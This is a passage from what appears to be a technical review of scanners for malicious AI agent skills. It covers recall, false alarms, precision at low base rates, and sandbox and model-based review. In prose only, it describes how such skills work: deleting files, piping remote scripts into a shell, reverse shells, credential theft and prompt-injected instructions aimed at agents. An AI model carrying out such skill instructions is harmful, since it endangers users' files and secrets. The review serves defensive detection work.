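| Destroying files on the user's machine | 11 | 0% |

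Code that steals data may read a secret, encode it and send it over the network, and a rule can look for each step or for the flow between them. But deleting a user's project folder takes only one ordinary call, the same one a clean-up script makes. None of the scanner's five checks flagged any of the 11 destructive skills. With so few samples, a scanner that caught one in five such attacks would still miss all 11 about 9% of the time, but the similarity to clean-up code makes a very low detection rate plausible.

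The result for remote scripts is more surprising, because a pattern for a download piped into a shell is easy to write. The scoring system is a likely cause. Each check contributes to a total between 0 and 100, and the scanner flags a skill at 25. The check for dangerous keywords has a weight of 0.15, so if no other check matches, the total can't exceed 15, however dangerous the command is. Only the data-flow check, with a weight of 0.30, can reach the threshold alone. The pattern may have matched many of the missed skills without raising their totals to 25. A weighted total suits attacks that leave several traces, but a rule pack that uses one should also let a few decisive rules flag a skill by themselves.

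The attacks in this test are also artificial. Chen and colleagues acknowledge that inserting attack code into a benign skill doesn't reproduce the disguise a determined attacker would use. Recall is probably lower against such attackers, since rewritten logic can evade static rules, as Wang, He and colleagues note. *MaliciousSkillBench* (Wang, Liu and colleagues, 2026) also cites work in which harmful workflows evaded scanners that inspect skills one at a time.

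*SkillVetBench* (2026) reports that, of 19 skills containing prompt injection, VirusTotal flagged none, ClawScan flagged three, and the language model under test flagged all 19.

### From 98,380 skills to 157

Liu, Chen and colleagues searched two registries for malicious skills instead of starting from a labelled set, so their results give an idea of how rare such skills are.

Their patterns left 4,287 of the 98,380 skills as candidates, and 762 of these did something suspicious in the sandbox. Two researchers reviewed all 762 and confirmed 157 as malicious, or 0.16% of the original collection. The registries later removed all 157.

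The confirmed skills contained 632 security problems, of which 84% were in SKILL.md and less than 9% in scripts. The researchers rightly conclude that defenders need to analyse natural language as well as code. However, only 209 of the 632 problems belong to the categories for prompts and instructions, so most of the problems in SKILL.md must be of other kinds, such as commands that download and run a script, the most common problem in the study. Text rules can match many of these if the scanner reads Markdown files.

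Recall on a set of real attacks can depend heavily on one campaign. One publisher produced 85 of the 157 skills from a single template. A rule that matched one line of that template would have a recall of 54% on this collection, even if it detected no other attack.

The figure of 157 is a minimum. The researchers later examined 413 of the unconfirmed candidates and found that 93% contained dormant code that the sandbox hadn't triggered. If the same share of all unconfirmed candidates were malicious, the total would be about 4,000, or 4% of the collection. But nobody saw the dormant code do any harm, and some of it may be benign.

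Two other large scans found similar rates of confirmed malicious skills. Wang, He and colleagues flagged 620 of 150,108 skills from seven registries and reviewed a random 100 of them, of which 76 were malicious. That suggests about 470 of the flagged skills were malicious, or 0.3% of all those scanned. In North Echo's *I Scanned 30,000 AI Agent Skills for Malware. Here's What I Found*, Christopher Lusk, a security engineer, describes running 28 rules on 30,037 ClawHub skills. He confirmed 43 as malicious, or 0.14%, and left another 401 marked "suspicious".

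### What rarity does to precision

Suppose that a marketplace has 100,000 skills and that 0.16% of them, or 160, are malicious. A scanner with a recall of 0.91 and a false-positive rate of 0.55, the figures for Cisco's scanner in the test by Truong-Le and colleagues, would give these results:

- malicious skills flagged: 160 × 0.91 ≈ 146
- benign skills flagged: 99,840 × 0.55 ≈ 54,900
- precision: 146 ÷ (146 + 54,900) ≈ 0.3%

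The scanner would raise about 376 false alarms for every malicious skill it found. North Echo reports reviewing 589 skills in about five hours. At that speed, one person would need nearly 12 weeks of full-time work to check all the flagged skills, and the scanner would still have missed 14 malicious ones.

The same calculation for other detectors shows how much the false-positive rate matters. The last two combine rules with other evidence.

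| Detector | Malicious flagged | Benign flagged | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| YARA | 146 | 81,900 | 0.2% |
| Cisco's scanner, rules only | 146 | 54,900 | 0.3% |
| Full system of Truong-Le and colleagues | 136 | 8,000 | 1.7% |
| SkillGate, the filter of Yang and colleagues | 123 | 1,130 | 10% |

The rates come from two different test sets, so the table isn't a fair ranking. It shows that a detector can look good in a test and still produce mostly false alarms. A scanner with a recall of 0.91 would need a false-positive rate of about 0.15%, or roughly one benign skill in 700, for half of the skills it flags to be malicious. A test with 60 benign skills can't measure a rate that low, because a single false alarm amounts to 1.7%.

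If all the dormant code were malicious, 4% of skills would be malicious, and the precision of Cisco's scanner would rise to about 6%. Yang and colleagues cite a report that 20% of ClawHub's skills were malicious in February 2026. At that share, precision would still be only 29%.

Liu, Chen and colleagues ran Cisco's scanner on their own collection of skills and estimated its precision at 1.1% at most, even assuming it caught every malicious skill they had confirmed.

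### Benign skills in a test and in a marketplace

The estimate of 54,900 false alarms assumes that the 60 benign test skills resemble those in a marketplace, which they may not. Truong-Le and colleagues collected 300 benign skills, 200 from a curated list and 100 from a benchmark. Curated skills are probably larger and more capable than the average marketplace listing, with more commands, network calls and keys for a rule to match.

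Results from Wang, He and colleagues suggest how large this effect can be. Their detector wrongly flagged 5 of the 100 popular benign skills in their test. At that rate, it would have raised about 7,500 false alarms on the 150,108 skills from the seven registries. It flagged only 620 of them, so its false-positive rate there was at most about 0.4%. If Cisco's scanner behaves similarly, the figure of 54,900 is far too high, though nobody has measured by how much.

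A few of the supposed false alarms may also be correct, because nobody independently checked the 200 skills from the curated list. Wang, Liu and colleagues were stricter when they combined 13 public sources into one benchmark. They accepted only 2,251 of 48,217 supposedly benign records, because they required the actual skill and reasonable evidence that it was harmless, and they didn't count a clean scan as evidence. They also excluded 34 skills that some sources had labelled malicious and others benign.

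Their results show why the source of the benign skills matters. They trained a simple word-based detector and tested it on skills from sources absent from its training data. It still caught 95.6% of the malicious skills but wrongly flagged 62.4% of the benign ones. It had probably learned the writing styles of its training sources, and so flagged skills written in unfamiliar ways. A team can only learn the false-positive rate for its own skills by measuring it on them.

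### Who gets flagged by mistake

Security tools are the most obvious source of false alarms. North Echo gives the clearest measurement for reverse shells. One rule flagged shell commands that use Bash's network path, and Lusk reviewed every skill it matched. Nine contained a real reverse shell, and the other 14 were legitimate security tools that included the pattern to detect it. The rule's precision was therefore 39%, much higher than that of a whole scanner but still too low to justify blocking skills without a review.

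Chen and colleagues found the same problem when they ran their scanner on the SKILL.md files of 138,133 real skills. It flagged 1.75%, and the highest scores went mostly to penetration-testing skills, antivirus scanners and similar tools. Running the code doesn't solve this either. Liu, Chen and colleagues ran skills in a sandbox, and reviewers didn't confirm 605 of the ones that looked suspicious. Most of those 605 were harmless tools such as credential managers and penetration-testing utilities.

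Of the 43 malicious skills that North Echo reports, 12 belonged to one campaign, and all 12 posed as security scanners. Exempting anything that calls itself a security tool would have let in the whole campaign.

Documentation causes many of the other false alarms. Liu, Chen and colleagues found that Cisco's scanner wrongly reported an example request in SKILL.md and a fake key in a test file as exposed passwords. Harmless code can also resemble an attack. A rule for Python's `compile`, which can prepare text to run as code, matched `re.compile`, which only prepares a regular expression.

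Skills that arrange for code to run later can also trigger false alarms. The false alarms that Wang, He and colleagues examined included skills with scheduled jobs, installation steps and environment settings. Their detector treats these features as relevant evidence because malicious skills use them too.

A single overly broad rule can produce most of the noise. In North Echo's scan of ClawHub, one rule for Base64 text produced about 175,000 of the 263,693 findings. Skills commonly use this encoding for images and configuration. Base64 in documentation was also the main cause of SkillGate's false alarms. Removing or narrowing such a rule can save reviewers more time than improving all the others.

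### What running the skill adds

Truong-Le and colleagues also built a system in which language models judge each skill using several kinds of evidence. They tested it on the same 140 skills with four combinations of evidence, using the same models each time.

| Evidence given to the models | Malicious skills found (of 80) | Benign skills flagged (of 60) | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Skill text only | 54 | 21 | 0.70 |
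| Skill text and static findings | 28 | 3 | 0.50 |
| Skill text and sandbox evidence | 63 | 5 | 0.85 |
| All three | 68 | 5 | 0.89 |

Sandbox evidence helped most. With it, the models found nine more malicious skills and raised 16 fewer false alarms than with the text alone. Adding static findings to the sandbox evidence helped them find another five malicious skills with no new false alarms.

In the sandbox, an agent tries to use the skill with harmless dummy data. It skips dangerous steps, such as sending out credentials, and records what the skill asked for. The system then scores each suspicious pattern by the strength of the evidence. A medium-severity pattern starts with 70 points and keeps them all if the agent carried out the action. If the skill's files contain the instruction but nothing ran, the pattern typically gets 70 × 0.70 = 49, which is still above the threshold of 35 for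 malicious behaviour. If the only evidence is a remark that the agent can't trace to the files, the score is capped at 25, which is below the threshold.

This grading reduces the confusion between a skill that performs an attack and one that only mentions it. It also means that the gain from 0.70 to 0.85 isn't purely a result of running code. The evidence included written output from the agent in the sandbox, Claude Opus 4.8. Different models, some of them much smaller, gave the verdict. Some of the improvement may come from a second model having read the skill.

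The system can still flag ordinary behaviour as malicious. One of its five false alarms was research-lookup, a skill whose instructions pipe an installation script from the vendor's website into a shell. The skill also sends an API key to the service it uses. Its sandbox score was 27.5, below the threshold, and one finding listed the installation command as benign. But the system finally classified the skill as malicious, with a score of 92 out of 100. The installation command is a risk, but it isn't evidence that the skill's author meant harm.

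### Why static findings lowered recall

Extra evidence reduced the number of malicious skills found from 54 to 28 (a recall of 0.35), which seems odd. Truong-Le and colleagues call the result conservative but don't test what caused it.

The most likely reason is the poor quality of the findings. They came from 58,674 general-purpose rules in OSS-Detect-Backdoor and YARA, mostly written for other kinds of malware. These tools had raised more alerts on the average benign skill, so a long list of findings was little help to the models. The models also had instructions not to treat a sensitive operation as proof of malice, so they may have classified malicious skills with many minor alerts as ordinary software. Being less likely to label any skill malicious would also explain why their false alarms fell from 21 to 3.

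The static findings may also have directed the models to the wrong place. The system uses flagged lines to decide what to investigate, and an attack written as plain instructions may not produce one. The models' median time on a skill fell from 320 seconds to 95 when they received static findings. It fell just as far with sandbox evidence, yet recall rose, so shorter investigations can't be the whole explanation. Chance probably can't account for the 26 extra misses, although the researchers ran each combination only once.

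Static rules had the opposite effect in Wang, He and colleagues' system. It uses 2,665 Semgrep rules to list operations such as reading a file or contacting a server, then links those that handle the same data. A language model judges the linked operations. Removing the rules and other parsing cut recall from 92% to 27%, while removing the model's judgement raised the false-positive rate from 5% to 49%.

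The two results are compatible because the rules in this system supply facts, such as which file the skill reads and where the data goes, while the general-purpose rules supplied alerts without that context. The drop to 27% also partly reflects the design, since the model relies on the list of operations and has little input when that list is nearly empty. A rule that reports the file, the address and the link between them gives the next reviewer more information than one that reports only "suspicious network activity".

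### Rules as the first filter

Sandboxes and language models are too slow to use on every skill. In Truong-Le and colleagues' system, the models took an average of 156 seconds per skill when given all the evidence, not counting the sandbox's time. At that rate, checking 100,000 skills one at a time would take about 180 days. If rules first selected 4.4% of them, the share that Liu, Chen and colleagues kept as candidates, checking those would take about eight days.

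SkillGate's regular expressions alone flagged 135 of the 150 malicious skills, but also 406 of the 1,500 benign ones. A language model then reviewed only the flagged skills.

| Stage | Recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|
| Regular expressions alone | 90% | 27.1% |
| Regular expressions, then the model | 77% | 1.13% |
| Model reads every file in full, without rules | 80% | 1.76% |

The model removed about 96% of the false alarms but also rejected about 15% of the correct matches. Recall in a tiered system is the product of the two stages' recalls, here 0.90 × 0.85 ≈ 0.77. Having the model read every file would have raised recall by about three percentage points but required 1,650 model calls instead of 540.

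The first filter should be broad because it caps the final recall. In tests by Chen and colleagues, static analysis with a threshold of 25 caught 28% of the remote-script attacks, while Claude Opus 4.6 recognised a threat in 53%. If only skills above that threshold went on to the model, most of those attacks would never reach it. The comparison is preliminary because the tests didn't use identical sets of samples.

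They also propose automatically blocking every skill that scores 45 or more and sending less certain cases to a model. Their own results are a reason not to block automatically. About 0.3% of the 138,133 real skills, roughly 400, scored that high, and the top scores belonged mostly to legitimate security tools, so high-scoring skills need a review of their purpose as much as the others do.

A tiered system also needs a way to discover what its first stage misses. One option is to also send a small random sample of unmatched skills through the sandbox and human review. If three of 1,000 sampled skills were malicious, the estimate for a marketplace with 95,000 unmatched skills would be roughly 285 malicious ones. Rule writers could use the three they found to decide which patterns to add.
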